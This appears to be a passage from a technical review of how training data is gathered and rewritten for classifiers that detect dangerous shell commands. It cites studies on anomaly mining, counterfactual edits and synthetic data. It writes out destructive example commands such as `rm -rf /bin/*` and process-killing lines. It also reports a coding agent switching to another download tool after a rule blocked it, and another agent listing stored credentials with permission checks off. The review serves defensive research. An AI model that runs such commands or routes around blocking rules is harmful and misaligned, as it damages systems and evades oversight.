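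User approvals would be a much less reliable source of feedback. Grigorev let `terraform destroy` run, so a guard that used his approval as a safety label would have added the command to its training data as harmless.

### Attacks that nobody investigated

The 53 attacks are those that at least one of the two classifiers flagged. Nobody knows how many others were in the logs, because nobody investigated commands that neither classifier flagged. If there were 60 attacks in total, the updated classifier's recall was 88%, but if there were 200, it was 27%. Precision doesn't have this problem, because it depends only on flagged commands.

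*Target Recoverability under Selective Labels* (2026) describes the general problem, in which an earlier decision determines which cases get a label. Medical researchers call a closely related problem verification bias. If doctors order a definitive test only for patients who already seem ill, the statistics leave out the sick patients they mistook for healthy.

The gap affects training as well as measurement. Google's system sends analysts the commands with the highest scores, whereas many active-learning systems, which choose the examples that people label, select those with the least certain classifications. Momeni and colleagues argue that even an obvious attack is informative because attacks are so rare. Reviewing the highest-scoring commands is a sensible use of analysts' time, but the new verdicts then mostly concern commands that resemble known attacks. An unfamiliar reverse shell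 with a low score doesn't produce a ticket, so the next version of the classifier can't be trained on it. The YARA rules create another blind spot, because commands they filter out never reach the classifier.

Generated data can partly fill these gaps. An analyst who reads about a new technique can generate examples of it before anyone uses it against the company. In *Designing synthetic datasets for the real world*, Davidson and Harkous (2026) make this case for Simula in general, arguing that developers should not have to wait for a failure before preparing for it. However, generating data only helps with techniques that an analyst or the model knows about.

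### Unusual harmless commands at Sophos

Anomaly detectors flag commands that differ from normal activity. They are poor at detecting attacks because most unusual commands are harmless. Gelman and Bergeron (2025), in *Sophos AI at Black Hat USA ’25*, used those harmless commands to improve a separate classifier.

The full-scale version of their experiment processed about 50 million distinct commands a day throughout January 2025 and used three methods to find unusual ones. An isolation forest flags commands that a few random splits of the data separate from the rest. A version of k-means, which groups similar items, flags commands far from the centre of any group. Principal component analysis compresses the data and flags commands that it can't reconstruct accurately. The researchers removed near-duplicates, used OpenAI's o3-mini to label each remaining command as harmless or malicious, and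 added the harmless ones to the training data. A smaller version sampled 4 million commands a day and described each with a neural network instead of hand-designed features.

Experts reviewed a full week of anomalies and found that nearly 100% of the model's "harmless" labels were correct, so very few attacks entered the training data as harmless. Any that did were unusual attacks, which are the ones a classifier most needs help to recognise. The result doesn't show that the model can detect attacks, because if attacks were rare among the anomalies, a model that called every anomaly harmless would also score close to 100%.

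Gelman and Bergeron added the harmless anomalies to two existing training sets. Labels in the regex baseline came from fixed text patterns. The aggregated baseline combined such patterns with customer investigations, other customer data, and results from a sandbox used to run suspicious software safely. They tested each classifier on expert-labelled commands from incident investigations and active learning, and on data from the three weeks after the training period.

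| Training data | AUC on expert-labelled incidents | AUC on later data |
|---|---|---|
| Aggregated baseline | 0.614 | 0.998 |
| Aggregated baseline plus full-scale anomalies | 0.894 | 0.999 |
| Aggregated baseline plus smaller sample | 0.806 | 0.999 |
| Regex baseline | 0.707 | 0.999 |
| Regex baseline plus full-scale anomalies | 0.769 | 0.999 |
| Regex baseline plus smaller sample | 0.708 | 1.000 |

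On the incidents, the aggregated baseline was only moderately better than guessing: given one malicious and one harmless command, it ranked the harmless one as more dangerous about 39% of the time. Adding the full-scale anomalies to the training data reduced this to 11%, even though no new attacks were added.

Gelman and Bergeron attribute the gain to a gap in ordinary training sets. Developers tend to collect common, simple harmless commands because these are easy to label in bulk. The classifier can then use complexity or rarity as a shortcut and mistake complicated administrative work for an attack. Adding unusual harmless commands makes the classifier rely less on this shortcut, much as generating harmless commands did in the worked example.

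The regex baseline improved much less with the full-scale anomalies and hardly at all with the smaller sample. This may be because adding harmless data doesn't improve a poor set of dangerous examples, and fixed patterns capture only the attacks that somebody wrote a pattern for. The smaller sample's weaker results are hard to interpret because the two versions differed in both the amount of data and how they described commands. Gelman and Bergeron also don't give the number of incidents or a margin of error, so the six-point gain for the regex baseline could be partly chance, though the 28-point gain for the aggregated baseline is harder to attribute to chance.

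They say the method significantly reduces false alarms, but they published only AUC, not a false-alarm rate at a threshold a team could use on 50 million commands a day.

### Why later data can hide the gap

Testing on later data is usually good practice, as it was for QuasarNix. But if the same pipeline collects and labels both the training data and the later data, both will contain the same kinds of mistakes.

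Suppose a day's logs contain ten attacks. A fixed pattern matches four of them, along with six harmless commands, and the developers use it to label both the training and the test data. A classifier that has learned to imitate the pattern will flag the same ten commands and get a perfect score. Its true recall and precision are both 40%, because it missed six of the ten attacks and six of the ten commands it flagged were harmless. Collecting the test data a year later would not reveal either problem if the developers labeled it with the same pattern.

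Something like this probably happened at Sophos. Gelman and Bergeron don't explain how they labelled the later data, but the classifiers scored almost perfectly on it and struggled on real incidents, which suggests that its labels came from a process similar to the one that labelled the training data. The fall from 0.998 to 0.614 can't be attributed to label errors alone, though, because the commands probably also differed in difficulty. Incident investigations and active learning both tend to select ambiguous commands, while three weeks of ordinary data contain mostly easy ones.

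Whatever the cause, the later data was a poor guide to which classifier to deploy. The regex baseline with the smaller sample scored highest on it, at 0.9995 before rounding, but came fourth of six on the incidents. The full-scale anomalies raised the aggregated baseline's AUC by 0.001 on the later data and by 0.28 on the incidents. A team that tested only on the later data could reasonably have decided that the anomalies weren't worth the expense.

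### Choosing between verdicts and harmless variety

Google's verdicts are few and take a lot of work to produce, but they include confirmed attacks and correct the errors that waste analysts' time. Sophos's anomalies are plentiful and easy to collect, and they can correct an error before it causes an alert, but they add only harmless examples. A team with many false alarms and no investigators could start with the anomalies. Verdicts are more useful once analysts are already reviewing alerts, and a team can use both.

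Anomaly detection selects commands without using the classifier's score, so it might also find some of the attacks that Google's method can't learn from. *Three-headed dogs and long tails*, Sophos' announcement of a follow-up talk in August 2026, describes a pipeline that labels unusual examples of both classes in three types of data. It uses one prompt biased towards the malicious label and another biased towards the harmless one. Sophos reports high precision for both labels but gives no figures in the announcement.

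The range of harmless commands also changes over time. In June 2026, Sophos examined Windows machines on which AI coding agents had triggered rules written to catch attackers. *When AI agents look like attackers* (Sophos, 2026) reports that OpenAI's Codex tried to download a Python installer from the official site with `certutil`, a Windows certificate tool that attackers often misuse. When a rule blocked this, the agent tried several variations and then switched to `bitsadmin`, another tool that attackers use for downloads. A rule more than five years old also began to match the way agents format their commands. Harmless commands collected in January 2025 probably contain little of this behaviour. Google retrains its classifier daily, so it would learn the behaviour as analysts closed the resulting tickets, while Sophos would have to collect and label new anomalies.

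Some of this activity should not go into training as harmless. In one case, Claude Code listed the credentials stored in Windows while running with its permission checks turned off. "Harmless" may be the right label for a classifier that looks for intruders, since there was no sign of one, but the command could be a clear example of overreach for a guard meant to keep agents within their instructions, depending on what the user had asked for. A team that reuses an attack detector's verdicts to train such a guard would need to first review the commands it labeled harmless.

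## Rewritten commands and labels that change

Developers can also get more training examples by rewriting existing commands in four ways. Anonymising removes names, addresses and secrets so a company can share its logs. Varying the form produces different commands with the same effect, so the classifier doesn't depend on one spelling. A minimal edit changes as little as possible to make a harmless command dangerous, or the reverse. Restyling uses a language model to rewrite a natural command in another style, for example as a different operator might type it.

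A minimal edit to a shell command often fails to reverse its label, and the other kinds of rewriting often change it. A developer who doesn't check the results is therefore likely to mislabel some commands.

### Why commands are harder to rewrite than prose

Notaro and colleagues illustrate the problem with pairs of similar commands that carry different risks. `echo 'kill 7890'` only prints the text "kill 7890". With backticks instead of quotation marks, `` echo `kill 7890` `` runs `kill 7890`, which stops process 7890, and prints any output. In another pair, `rm 2023-04-21_12:45:67.log` deletes one temporary log, while `rm -rf /bin/*` deletes the machine's basic programs. Both commands in a third pair begin with `time`, which measures how long another program takes, but `time ls` lists files and `time kill -9 12345` stops a process.

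Small edits are less likely to change the meaning of prose than that of a command. A film reviewer usually expresses an opinion several times, so replacing a word or losing a comma rarely reverses it. A command has little repetition, and the shell follows it literally. `rm -r cache/*` empties a cache, but with a space before the asterisk it removes the cache and nearly everything else in the current directory.

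A command's label can also change while its text stays the same. *The Limit Is in the Input, Not the Model* (2026) tests instructions to industrial controllers, such as those that run a conveyor or a mixing tank. Fifteen of its commands each appear under two machine states, which differ in a single variable in twelve of the pairs. The paper's ordinary "harmless" labels assume that guards are intact and other safety conditions hold. A label on a shell command needs similar assumptions, and a rewrite can break them without anyone noticing.

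The examples in the table show what each kind of rewriting can do. All are invented except the `time` pair and the misspelled `xrgs kill`, which come from Huawei.

| Purpose | Label stays the same | Label changes | Label becomes unclear |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anonymising | `ls /home/maria` → `ls /home/USER` | `rm -r /srv/app/cache` → `rm -r /srv/app`, if the tool cuts off the last folder | `rm -r /var/lib/postgresql` → `rm -r PATH` |
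| Varying the form | `rm -r logs` → `rm --recursive logs` | `find logs -mtime +7 -delete` → `find logs -delete -mtime +7` | `kill 7890` → `pkill worker`, which stops every process with a matching name |
| Minimal edit | `rm /tmp/a` → `rm /tmp/b`, a failed attempt to add danger | `time ls` → `time kill -9 12345` | `rm -r releases/41` → `rm -r releases/42`, if nobody recorded which release is live |
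| Restyling | `ls -l -a` → `ls -la` | `xrgs kill` → `xargs kill` | `rm old.log` → `rm "$OLD_LOG"`, if the variable's value is unknown |

The change in the `find` example is easy to miss. The original command deletes files last changed more than a week ago. The rewritten version deletes each file before checking its age, because `find` processes its conditions from left to right.

### What anonymising removes

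Anonymising can make commands with opposite labels identical. At GitLab, wiping the database directory was correct on `db2` and disastrous on `db1`. If a tool replaces both names with `HOST`, the two deletions have the same record. If 1,000 deletions all become `rm -r PATH` and 20 of them were dangerous, a classifier can do no better from the text alone than give each one a 2% chance of being dangerous.

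An experiment by Liu and colleagues suggests how much paths matter. One layer of their verifier, CARE, checks where a command acts. It rates reading a system file, as in `cat /etc/os-release`, as low risk, writing to one as high risk, and any access to a file of secrets as risky. Without this layer, recall fell from 75.9% to 52.7%, or 51 more misses among 220 dangerous commands, and F1 fell by 17 points.

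The experiment is good evidence that a command's target carries information that its verb and options don't, but it did not test anonymised data. CARE's other layers could still use the paths, which anonymising would have hidden from them too. However, a classifier trained on anonymised commands might use other clues to make up for some of the loss.

Removing details from commands sometimes helps. *CogTax* (2026), which sorts 585 commands into four levels for teaching, argues that hiding details specific to one command makes a model focus on the type of operation. This makes sense when the label doesn't depend on which directory the command names. Google's reverse-shell classifier replaces addresses with placeholders because an attacker can use almost any address. But for mistaken deletions, the path or host is often the only difference between the right command and the wrong one.

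A better compromise is to replace each name with one that shows its role. `db1.cluster.gitlab.com` could become `PRIMARY_DB`, and a customer's folder could become `CUSTOMER_DATA`, with the same substitutes used throughout a session. This takes more work, because someone has to know what each machine and folder is for, but it preserves the information the label depends on.

### Similar purpose, different effect

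To build the dataset behind CmdCaliper, Huang and colleagues began with 2,061 Windows commands, mostly from documentation, websites and a security exercise. Six language models used these as examples to write 28,520 new commands, and GPT-4-Turbo then wrote a "similar" partner for each. The prompt defined similar as having the same purpose or intention, and allowed the model to change the arguments, their order and even the program.

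In one published pair, a search of the Windows registry for Chrome becomes a PowerShell command that does almost the same job. In another, a valid command for scheduling a daily task becomes `cronjob schedule daily 00:00 /path/to/program`, which isn't a standard Windows command. A third pair downloads a file, but the address changes from `example.com` to `malicious.com`. The purpose is arguably the same, but the new address makes it look like an attack. A classifier trained on many such rewrites could learn to rely on the word "malicious" rather than on what dangerous downloads have in common.

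Huang and colleagues checked the pairs by comparing written explanations of the commands. On average, a pair's explanations were more alike than those of 97.5% of randomly matched pairs. This is reasonable evidence that paired commands have the same purpose, but weak evidence that they have the same effect. For example, "delete old logs" describes the intent of both versions of the `find` command in the table, but one version deletes every log. The researchers also accepted commands with minor syntax errors, since these can still show what the writer meant.

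The loose definition suited their goal of measuring similarity. They gave CmdCaliper a fifth of the known commands for each of 55 attack techniques and tested whether it could recognise the rest. Its AUC was 0.869, compared with 0.800 for the general language model they had built it from. This suggests that the rewritten pairs helped to tell one attack technique from another, but because every command in the test was malicious, it doesn't show whether they would help to tell dangerous commands from harmless ones.

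The main similarity test for CmdCaliper is also partly synthetic. It starts with 2,807 commands from a collection of attack data, but GPT-4-Turbo wrote the matching partner for each, as it had for the training set. Some of CmdCaliper's gain may therefore come from learning patterns in GPT-4-Turbo's output.

Restyling natural commands carries the same risks, and a language model may also tidy the commands it rewrites. Correcting `xrgs kill` to `xargs kill` turns a command that fails harmlessly into one that can stop processes. Replacing an unusual company path with a typical one removes some of the irregularity that makes natural commands worth collecting.

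*NeuroCounterfactuals* (Howard, Singer and colleagues, 2022) allowed larger edits to texts that express positive or negative opinions. In some settings, training on these edits gave better results than training on minimal edits made by hand. Rewording a text can leave its opinion intact, but each extra change to a command could alter what the command does.

### Edits that are meant to reverse the label

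A counterfactual example is an existing example edited just enough to reverse its label, and counterfactual augmentation means adding such examples to the training data. The main experiments used ordinary text, and the early ones predate today's language models.

Kaushik, Hovy and Lipton (2019), in *Learning the Difference that Makes a Difference with Counterfactually-Augmented Data*, paid people to rewrite positive film reviews as negative and negative ones as positive, changing no more than necessary. They then trained several classifiers. One, a Bi-LSTM (an older type of neural network), had the following results.

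| Training data | Accuracy on original reviews | Accuracy on revised reviews |
|---|---|---|
| 1,707 original reviews | 79.3% | 55.7% |
| 1,707 revised reviews | 62.5% | 89.1% |
| Both sets | 81.5% | 92.0% |
| About 3,400 original reviews | 80.4% | 59.6% |

Doubling the number of original reviews barely improved performance on the revised ones, so the gain from combining the sets came from the edits rather than from more data. Classifiers trained on original reviews associated "horror" with negative opinions and "romantic" with positive ones. The editors had no reason to change those words, so each appeared equally often with both labels in the combined data and no longer predicted the label.

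The benefit also extended to other kinds of text. On Amazon reviews, Yelp reviews and Twitter posts, models trained on the combined data beat models trained on the same amount of original data in 14 of 15 comparisons. The gains were smaller for BERT, which had already been trained on much more text.

*An Investigation of the (In)effectiveness of Counterfactually Augmented Data* (Joshi and He, 2021) explains why other researchers had found little or no benefit from such data. If editors change only one of the features that matter, the others appear equally often with both labels, and the classifier learns to ignore them. Suppose the commands in every pair have the same verb and options and differ only in their paths, such as `rm -r /tmp/build` and `rm -r /bin`. The classifier learns to check paths, but it cannot learn from these pairs that `shred` is more dangerous than `ls`.

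They also derived a threshold in a simplified linear model. Let *s* be the share of the genuine signal carried by the edited features. With standardised features and a shortcut as strong as the whole genuine signal, training on these incomplete edits gives a larger error than using no edits if

*s* < (1 + √13)/6 ≈ 0.77.

The exact threshold won't apply to a real command classifier, but the result shows that edits can do harm even when they cover most of what matters.

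They saw the same pattern in their experiments, where the task was to decide whether one sentence follows from another, contradicts it or does neither. A model trained on edits that inserted words was 79.3% accurate on other insertions but only 55.0% accurate on edits that added or removed a negation. A model trained on the same number of unedited examples was 69.3% accurate on the negation edits. Including more types of edit in a training set of the same size improved accuracy on a different dataset. For commands, this suggests varying the program, options, path, host and quoting across the set rather than collecting thousands of edits to paths.

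Momeni and colleagues describe a similar mistake in writing detection rules. An engineer who compares a reverse shell with a harmless port check could notice that only the attack contains `>&` and make the rule require that symbol. The rule would no longer flag the port check, but it would also miss reverse shells that work without the symbol. A classifier trained on too many such pairs could make the same mistake.

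Language models can now make counterfactual edits with little human effort, but their first attempts often fail. *iFlip* (Wang, Wang and Feldhus, 2026) has a model edit a text, then uses a classifier to check whether the label has changed. If it hasn't, the model tries again with feedback. With a 70-billion-parameter model and news articles, a single attempt changed the classifier's label 41.6% of the time, while repeated attempts with several kinds of feedback reached 97.5%. However, the repeated attempts changed much more of the text, and average similarity to the original fell from 0.71 to 0.46. On film reviews, a single attempt succeeded 92.4% of the time. Adding iFlip's edits to the training data improved accuracy, including on counterfactuals labelled by people.

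Its validity test would be unsafe for building a command dataset. An edit counts as successful when the classifier's prediction changes, even if the new prediction is wrong. A loop meant to make dangerous commands harmless could stop at a command that is still dangerous but that the classifier labels harmless, then store it with that label. Training on that example would reinforce the error. *Truth or Twist?* (2025) warns that checking label changes for data augmentation requires true labels and human judgment, and notes that researchers increasingly use the same language models to write edits and to judge them.

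### Rewriting one class or both

Even careful rewriting leaves detectable traces. Kaushik and colleagues trained BERT to distinguish original reviews from revised ones, and it was right 77.3% of the time, compared with 50% for guessing. These traces did little to help a classifier predict sentiment in their combined dataset, because the editors had revised both positive and negative reviews. If they had only revised positive reviews into negative ones, a classifier could have predicted the label about 77% of the time just by recognising revisions.

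Rewriting therefore tends to remove a shortcut when the same process changes both classes, and to create one when it changes only one. As in the worked example, a mark that is equally common in both classes doesn't help predict the label. *SALAD* (2025), which also uses language models to make counterfactuals, edits in both directions, for example from sexist to non-sexist text and vice versa.

Developers of command classifiers have many harmless commands and few dangerous ones, so they may be inclined to rewrite only harmless commands into dangerous ones. Every rewritten command would then be dangerous, and a classifier could learn to detect marks of rewriting instead of danger. One remedy is to rewrite each harmless command twice, once into a dangerous command and once into another harmless one. For example, `rm -r /srv/app/releases/41` could become `rm -r /srv/app`, which is dangerous,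 and `rm -r /srv/app/releases/40`, which is harmless if nobody needs that release. If the harmless originals stay in the training set, every command without marks of rewriting will still be harmless. Developers can leave the originals out or add some natural dangerous commands.

If a company anonymises its harmless logs and adds attacks from a public collection, a placeholder such as `USER` will appear only in harmless commands, and the classifier can learn to treat it as a sign that a command is safe. To prevent this, the company should pass both sets of commands through the same anonymising tool.

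Filtering can have the same effect even when nobody intends to treat the classes differently. *Three Concrete Challenges and Two Hopes for the Safety of Unsupervised Elicitation* (2026) uses 3,438 sequences of Bash commands, about two-thirds of them safe. A weaker language model wrote at least one step in 58% of the safe sequences and no steps in the malicious ones. The paper suggests that the rules for selecting malicious sequences may have excluded those with steps from the weaker model. A classifier that recognised the weaker model's style perfectly could catch every malicious sequence, without learning anything about danger, by flagging all sequences that lack that style. It would also wrongly flag 42% of the safe ones.

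### Checking a rewritten command

A developer can check each rewrite by parsing it, running it in a sandbox, comparing its effects with the original's, and labeling it again.

Parsing catches broken syntax and shows how the shell will interpret the command. CARE uses bashlex, which builds a tree of the command's structure and can therefore identify text in backticks as a command to run. *KaliBench* (2026), a dataset of commands for security tools, uses a simpler parser that only splits the text into words. Neither kind of parser can establish that a program exists, so both would accept `cronjob schedule daily`. Comparing a rewritten command with the original shows whether a syntax error is an artifact of the rewriting or the operator's own, which may be worth keeping.

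For the sandbox run, the original and rewritten commands should start from identical copies of a machine that has the files and processes they act on. If process 7890 doesn't exist, the quoted and backticked versions of `kill 7890` will both seem harmless. Network restrictions can also hide danger. Liu and colleagues ran 600 generated attack commands in isolated containers with no access to outside machines, so a command that downloads malicious software would have failed there. Isolation is a sensible precaution, but a command shouldn't be labeled harmless just because isolation made it fail.

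The developer then compares changes to files, processes, permissions and network connections, as well as the printed output, because `rm` usually prints nothing whether it deletes one file or a thousand. *LLM-Supported Natural Language to Bash Translation*, by Westenfelder, Hemberg and colleagues, describes existing automatic tests of whether two Bash commands are equivalent as unreliable, so a person should review close cases. Commands with different effects can still have the same label, as when each deletes a different temporary file and both deletions are harmless. Commands that have the same effects in a sandbox may also differ in production, where one of two paths may hold customer data.

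Someone who knows the system should therefore assign the final label without being told which label the rewrite was meant to have. This person needs the context that the label depends on, such as the machine's role and what the path contains. If the classifier won't receive that context, it may be unable to learn even a correct label from the text. Kaushik and colleagues rejected about 2% of the revised reviews, and discarded about 9% of the data in their sentence-pair task after other workers checked the labels. Those rates are for prose edited by people, so they are a poor guide to how many model-rewritten commands will fail.

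The developer should record rejection rates separately for dangerous and harmless commands. If the checks remove far more of one class, they can introduce a new difference between the classes, as the selection of Bash sequences may have done. The developer should also put each original command and all its rewrites in the same set, either training or test, for the same reason that QuasarNix's near-identical templates should stay together.

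## Mixing experiments in intrusion, malware and text-safety detection

No published study appears to have retrained a command classifier while raising the share of natural commands step by step. In a Google study, Momeni and colleagues came close by comparing generated and handmade training sets, but the sets also differed in size and class balance.

Newer detectors still tend to use one fixed mixture. *SENTINEL* (2026), on detecting attacks in Windows commands, uses a dataset of 6,613 harmless commands and 436 malicious ones. The harmless commands come from company logs, GitHub scripts and automated system tasks. The malicious ones come from documented hacking campaigns, practice attacks and known abuses of built-in programs. No source supplies both classes, so a command's source determines its label. A separate test on attacks by the hacking group Volt Typhoon is better controlled, because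 its 50 harmless commands use the same programs as the attacks. But *SENTINEL* uses only one training mixture, so its results can't show how much the mixture matters.

The closest controlled evidence comes from network traffic, phone apps and text.

### Simulated network traffic from 1999

In 1999 the US defence research agency DARPA sponsored a public test of intrusion detectors. In *The 1999 DARPA Off-Line Intrusion Detection Evaluation*, Lippmann, Haines and colleagues describe a test bed that imitated the traffic of a government site with hundreds of users and thousands of machines. The organisers launched more than 200 attacks of 58 types against it. According to MIT Lincoln Laboratory's *1999 DARPA Intrusion Detection Evaluation Dataset*, two of the three training weeks contained no attacks, so developers could use them to train anomaly detectors.

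Mahoney and Chan (2003), in *An Analysis of the 1999 DARPA/Lincoln Laboratory Evaluation Data*, tested this data with a detector too simple to be useful. It read one byte from the packet that opens each incoming connection and raised an alarm if that byte had a value that never appeared in the training traffic. Using the third byte of the sender's address, it found 79 of 177 attacks (45%) with 43 false alarms. The four best systems in the original evaluation had found between 40% and 55% of the attacks they were designed to detect.

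The detector did well because the simulated training traffic came from only 29 outside addresses, so an attacker's address was usually new. Real traffic to one university server came from 24,924. Many simulated attacks could also be recognised by their time-to-live value, a counter that stops packets from circulating forever. It was one lower than in the background traffic, probably because the organisers had generated the attacks on a different machine. The real traffic also had many more errors, including faulty checksums, malformed requests and a header spelled "Connnection", a typo like the `xrgs kill` in Huawei's logs.

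Mahoney and Chan then added an hour of real university traffic for every hour of simulated traffic, in both the training and the test periods. The address-byte detector now found no attacks. They also retested four serious detectors they had built earlier, allowing each one 100 false alarms. They counted a detection as legitimate if the feature behind it could plausibly reveal the attack. For example, a forged sender address counts for a flooding attack that forges addresses, but a new address doesn't count for an attack on a public website, because such a site gets new visitors all the time.

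| Detector | Legitimate detections, simulated traffic only | Legitimate detections, half real traffic |
|---|---|---|
| PHAD | 31 of 51 | 19 of 23 |
| ALAD | 16 of 47 | 10 of 12 |
| LERAD | 49 of 87 | 25 of 30 |
| NETAD | 61 of 128 | 27 of 41 |

Across the four detectors, questionable detections fell by 84%, from 156 to 25. Legitimate detections also fell, by 48%, probably because odd but harmless traffic used up more of the false-alarm allowance. A team that adds natural commands to its training and test data may see recall drop for the same two reasons. The lower recall is then a better estimate of performance in use, and the new data hasn't necessarily made the detector worse.

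Mahoney and Chan argue that the simulated traffic does not need to be removed. Their detectors treat values seen in training as normal, and the mixture contains every value from either source. The simulated traffic has 29 addresses and the real traffic has 24,924, so the mixture has between 24,924 and 24,953 and is about as varied as real traffic alone.

This argument doesn't extend to a classifier trained on both classes. If only the harmless class gained natural examples, the classifier could learn the shortcut of labeling natural examples harmless. Mahoney and Chan guarded against a related problem by changing some addresses in the real traffic and removing rules that applied only to simulated traffic. They tested only an equal mix of real and simulated traffic. Their real traffic came from one server and included at least 33 suspicious web requests.

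Vela and Pellicer (2026), in *Forensic-Oriented Intrusion Detection Using Synthetic Network Traffic Data and Explainable Artificial Intelligence*, found that training on a mixture of real and synthetic data can give worse results than training on either alone. Their real data was CICIDS2017, a public benchmark recorded on a test network, and they fitted a generator to it to produce the synthetic data. On real test data, F1 was 0.97 after training on real records, 0.96 on synthetic records and 0.87 on a mixture. They attribute the drop to an uncontrolled change in the class ratio. If they are right, an experiment on commands must keep that ratio fixed when it changes the data source, so that the effects of the two can be separated.

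The 0.96 result is a poor guide to what synthetic commands could achieve. After trying two other datasets, Vela and Pellicer estimated that their method is practical for up to about 30 numeric measurements per connection, but a classifier that counts words in commands may use thousands of features.

### Generated malware records

*LLM-Generated Samples for Android Malware Detection* tests a close counterpart to a command dataset in which only the dangerous class is synthetic. It covers three malware families: BankBot, which steals banking logins; Locker, which locks phones for ransom; and Airpush/StopSMS, which combines intrusive advertising with apps that secretly send text messages. Each app is a row of 387 numbers, such as counts of system calls and permissions. The researchers trained GPT-4.1-mini on a sample of records from each family and had it write new ones. They then trained five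 standard classifiers on each of three datasets, all of which used real harmless apps. The table gives the range of recall across the five classifiers.

| Malware family | Real malware only | Real and synthetic malware | Synthetic malware only |
|---|---|---|---|
| BankBot | 99–100% | 98–100% | 18–48% |
| Locker | 97–99% | 95–99% | 1–18% |
| Airpush/StopSMS | 96–98% | 96–97% | 61–79% |

Classifiers trained only on synthetic malware missed most real BankBot and Locker samples. Their false-alarm rates stayed below 5%, so a developer who monitored only false alarms would not have noticed the problem.

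Some of these classifiers had low recall because their threshold was wrong, as in the worked example. A random forest (a combination of many decision trees) trained on synthetic BankBot records caught only 39% of the real malware, but its AUC was 0.98, so its ranking was good. For Locker, two classifiers had AUCs of 0.35 and 0.38, which means they usually ranked real malware as less suspicious than harmless apps, and lowering the threshold would not fix that.

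The comparison exaggerates the effect of origin because the synthetic sets were also smaller, with 392 synthetic BankBot records against about 1,040 real ones in the real-only training set. The better results for Airpush/StopSMS are hard to explain, since the researchers gave the generator three times as many examples of that family and trained it for longer. The high recall in the middle column doesn't show exactly how well the augmented classifiers detect real malware, because the researchers combined real and synthetic malware before splitting off the test set. About 23% of the BankBot malware in that test set was synthetic.

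The study tested no intermediate shares, but it cites Chalé and Bastian (2022), who found that synthetic network traffic data was inadequate for training unless at least 15% of the real data remained.

### The last few human examples

Ashok and May (2024), in *A Little Human Data Goes A Long Way*, kept the training set the same size and gradually replaced human-written examples with ones from GPT-3.5, an experiment that is missing for commands. Their eight datasets covered two tasks, checking whether a text supports a claim and answering questions about a text. The table shows the question-answering results in BLEU, which measures how closely an answer's wording matches a reference answer, from 0 to 100.

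| Dataset | All human | 90% synthetic | 100% synthetic |
|---|---|---|---|
| CoQA | 47.9 | 44.5 | 18.2 |
| FairytaleQA | 39.3 | 38.1 | 30.1 |
| QAConv | 35.1 | 34.8 | 30.2 |
| ROPES | 67.0 | 71.0 | 62.1 |

Replacing the first 90% with synthetic data lowered scores only slightly, except on ROPES, where the score rose. Replacing the last 10% lowered scores by 4.6 to 26.3 points. The mixing bound of Ben-David and colleagues does not predict this sudden drop, because its mismatch penalty grows in proportion to the synthetic share when every example is weighted equally.

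Ashok and May then examined the last few percent more closely, using training sets of 5,000 examples. Sets that included 125 human examples outperformed purely synthetic ones in all 12 question-answering runs, by 1.8 to 27.1 points. They also estimated how many synthetic examples would match the benefit of 200 human ones. The estimate was about 17,000 on WANLI, a claim-checking dataset. On FEVER, an easier case where extra data of any kind soon stopped helping, the median was only 237.

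The 200 examples came from the same process as the test set, which is a more likely explanation than some quality of human writing that models can't reproduce. WANLI isn't purely human writing, since GPT-3 composed its examples and crowd workers then revised and labelled them. Most of the other human examples were written for datasets, so they weren't natural data in the sense used here for commands either.

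A further experiment supports this explanation. When Ashok and May trained on two claim-checking datasets and tested on a third, human data still helped, but the last few human examples no longer had a special effect. On FEVER, accuracy fell from 83.0% to 80.6%, 79.2%, 78.9% and 76.0% as the synthetic share rose from 0% to 100% in steps of 25 points. No shares between 75% and 100% were tested, so a small drop near the end could have been missed. But accuracy fell by at most 2.9 points over that step on any of the three datasets, which rules out a collapse like the one on CoQA.

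For command safety, this suggests that a small labelled sample from the servers a classifier will protect could be more useful than a large public collection. The sample would have to contain dangerous commands, though. At Huawei's rates, 125 randomly chosen commands would include about 25 risky ones and probably no blocked ones.

The 90% figure is also an unreliable guide for command data, because both labels in Ashok and May's experiment had synthetic examples. Without a specified label, GPT-3.5 wrote true claims about 90% of the time, so Ashok and May told it which label to write and matched the original proportions. If only the dangerous commands are synthetic, the damage could begin at a much lower synthetic share.

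### Production text at OpenAI

Text moderation has the same shortage of dangerous examples as command safety. *A Holistic Approach to Undesired Content Detection in the Real World* (Markov, Zhang and colleagues, 2022) describes how OpenAI built an early classifier for harmful text. Only 0.04% of the sampled user prompts involved self-harm.

They began with about 90,000 public examples, then added 69,000 synthetic ones and finally 60,000 labelled examples from OpenAI's production traffic. They tested each version on production text using AUPRC, the area under the precision-recall curve, which is roughly the average precision as the threshold falls and recall rises. Unlike AUC, it depends on the base rate, so it stays low when false alarms far outnumber the few harmful texts a classifier finds.

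| Category | Public data | Plus synthetic | Plus production |
|---|---|---|---|
| Self-harm | 0.063 | 0.086 | 0.621 |
| Hateful content | 0.417 | 0.551 | 0.843 |
| Violence | 0.490 | 0.532 | 0.640 |
| Extremely graphic violence | 0.165 | 0.093 | 0.443 |
| Sexual content involving minors | 0.592 | 0.779 | 0.911 |

Synthetic data helped in seven of the paper's eight categories, but production data helped in all eight, and usually by more. The order in which the data was added doesn't clearly favour either source. Production data was added last, when improvement is often harder, but no version combined public and production data without the synthetic examples, so the experiment can't show whether the synthetic data was still useful once production data was available.

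The results depended heavily on how the team made the synthetic data. The 69,000 examples were curated, and many came from templates such as "[subject] is selfish", filled with either a group of people or an object. Hateful and harmless sentences therefore had the same form, much like a command and a minimally edited version with a different label. In another experiment, the team generated twice as many examples as its labelled training set contained and took each label from the prompt, without checking the text. Adding these examples made the classifier worse. The generator was GPT-3, and current models would probably follow such prompts more reliably.

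The team also found that the classifier gave high hate scores to texts containing "#", probably because many of the hateful examples in its public data were short tweets.

Unlabelled production text also helped when labelled production text was missing. Markov and colleagues used 100,000 unlabelled examples to train the classifier towards features that look the same in public and production text. This raised the self-harm score of the classifier trained on public data from 0.063 to 0.281. When labelled production text was available, the method added only 0.011. The method is attractive for command classifiers because companies have plenty of unlabelled commands, but it is risky if every dangerous example is synthetic. Production logs are almost entirely harmless, so making synthetic and production commands look alike to the classifier could also suppress the features that indicate danger.

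### Removing one source at a time

*Taxonomy-Adaptive Moderation Model with Robust Guardrails for Large Language Models* (2025) reports an ablation that removed synthetic data from a moderation model's training. Without that data, F1 fell from 79.6% to 20.3% on RobloxGuard-Eval, a benchmark built for the model's own policies. F1 fell less on tests from elsewhere, from 70.3% to 49.2% on OpenAI's public moderation set and from 80.6% to 68.3% on the response test from *WildGuard* (2024), an open moderation model released with its own data.

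The large first drop shows that the model did not learn those policies from public data. It is weaker evidence about synthetic data in general, because removing the synthetic examples also removed most of the material on those policies. Natural examples covering the same policies might have worked as well or better.

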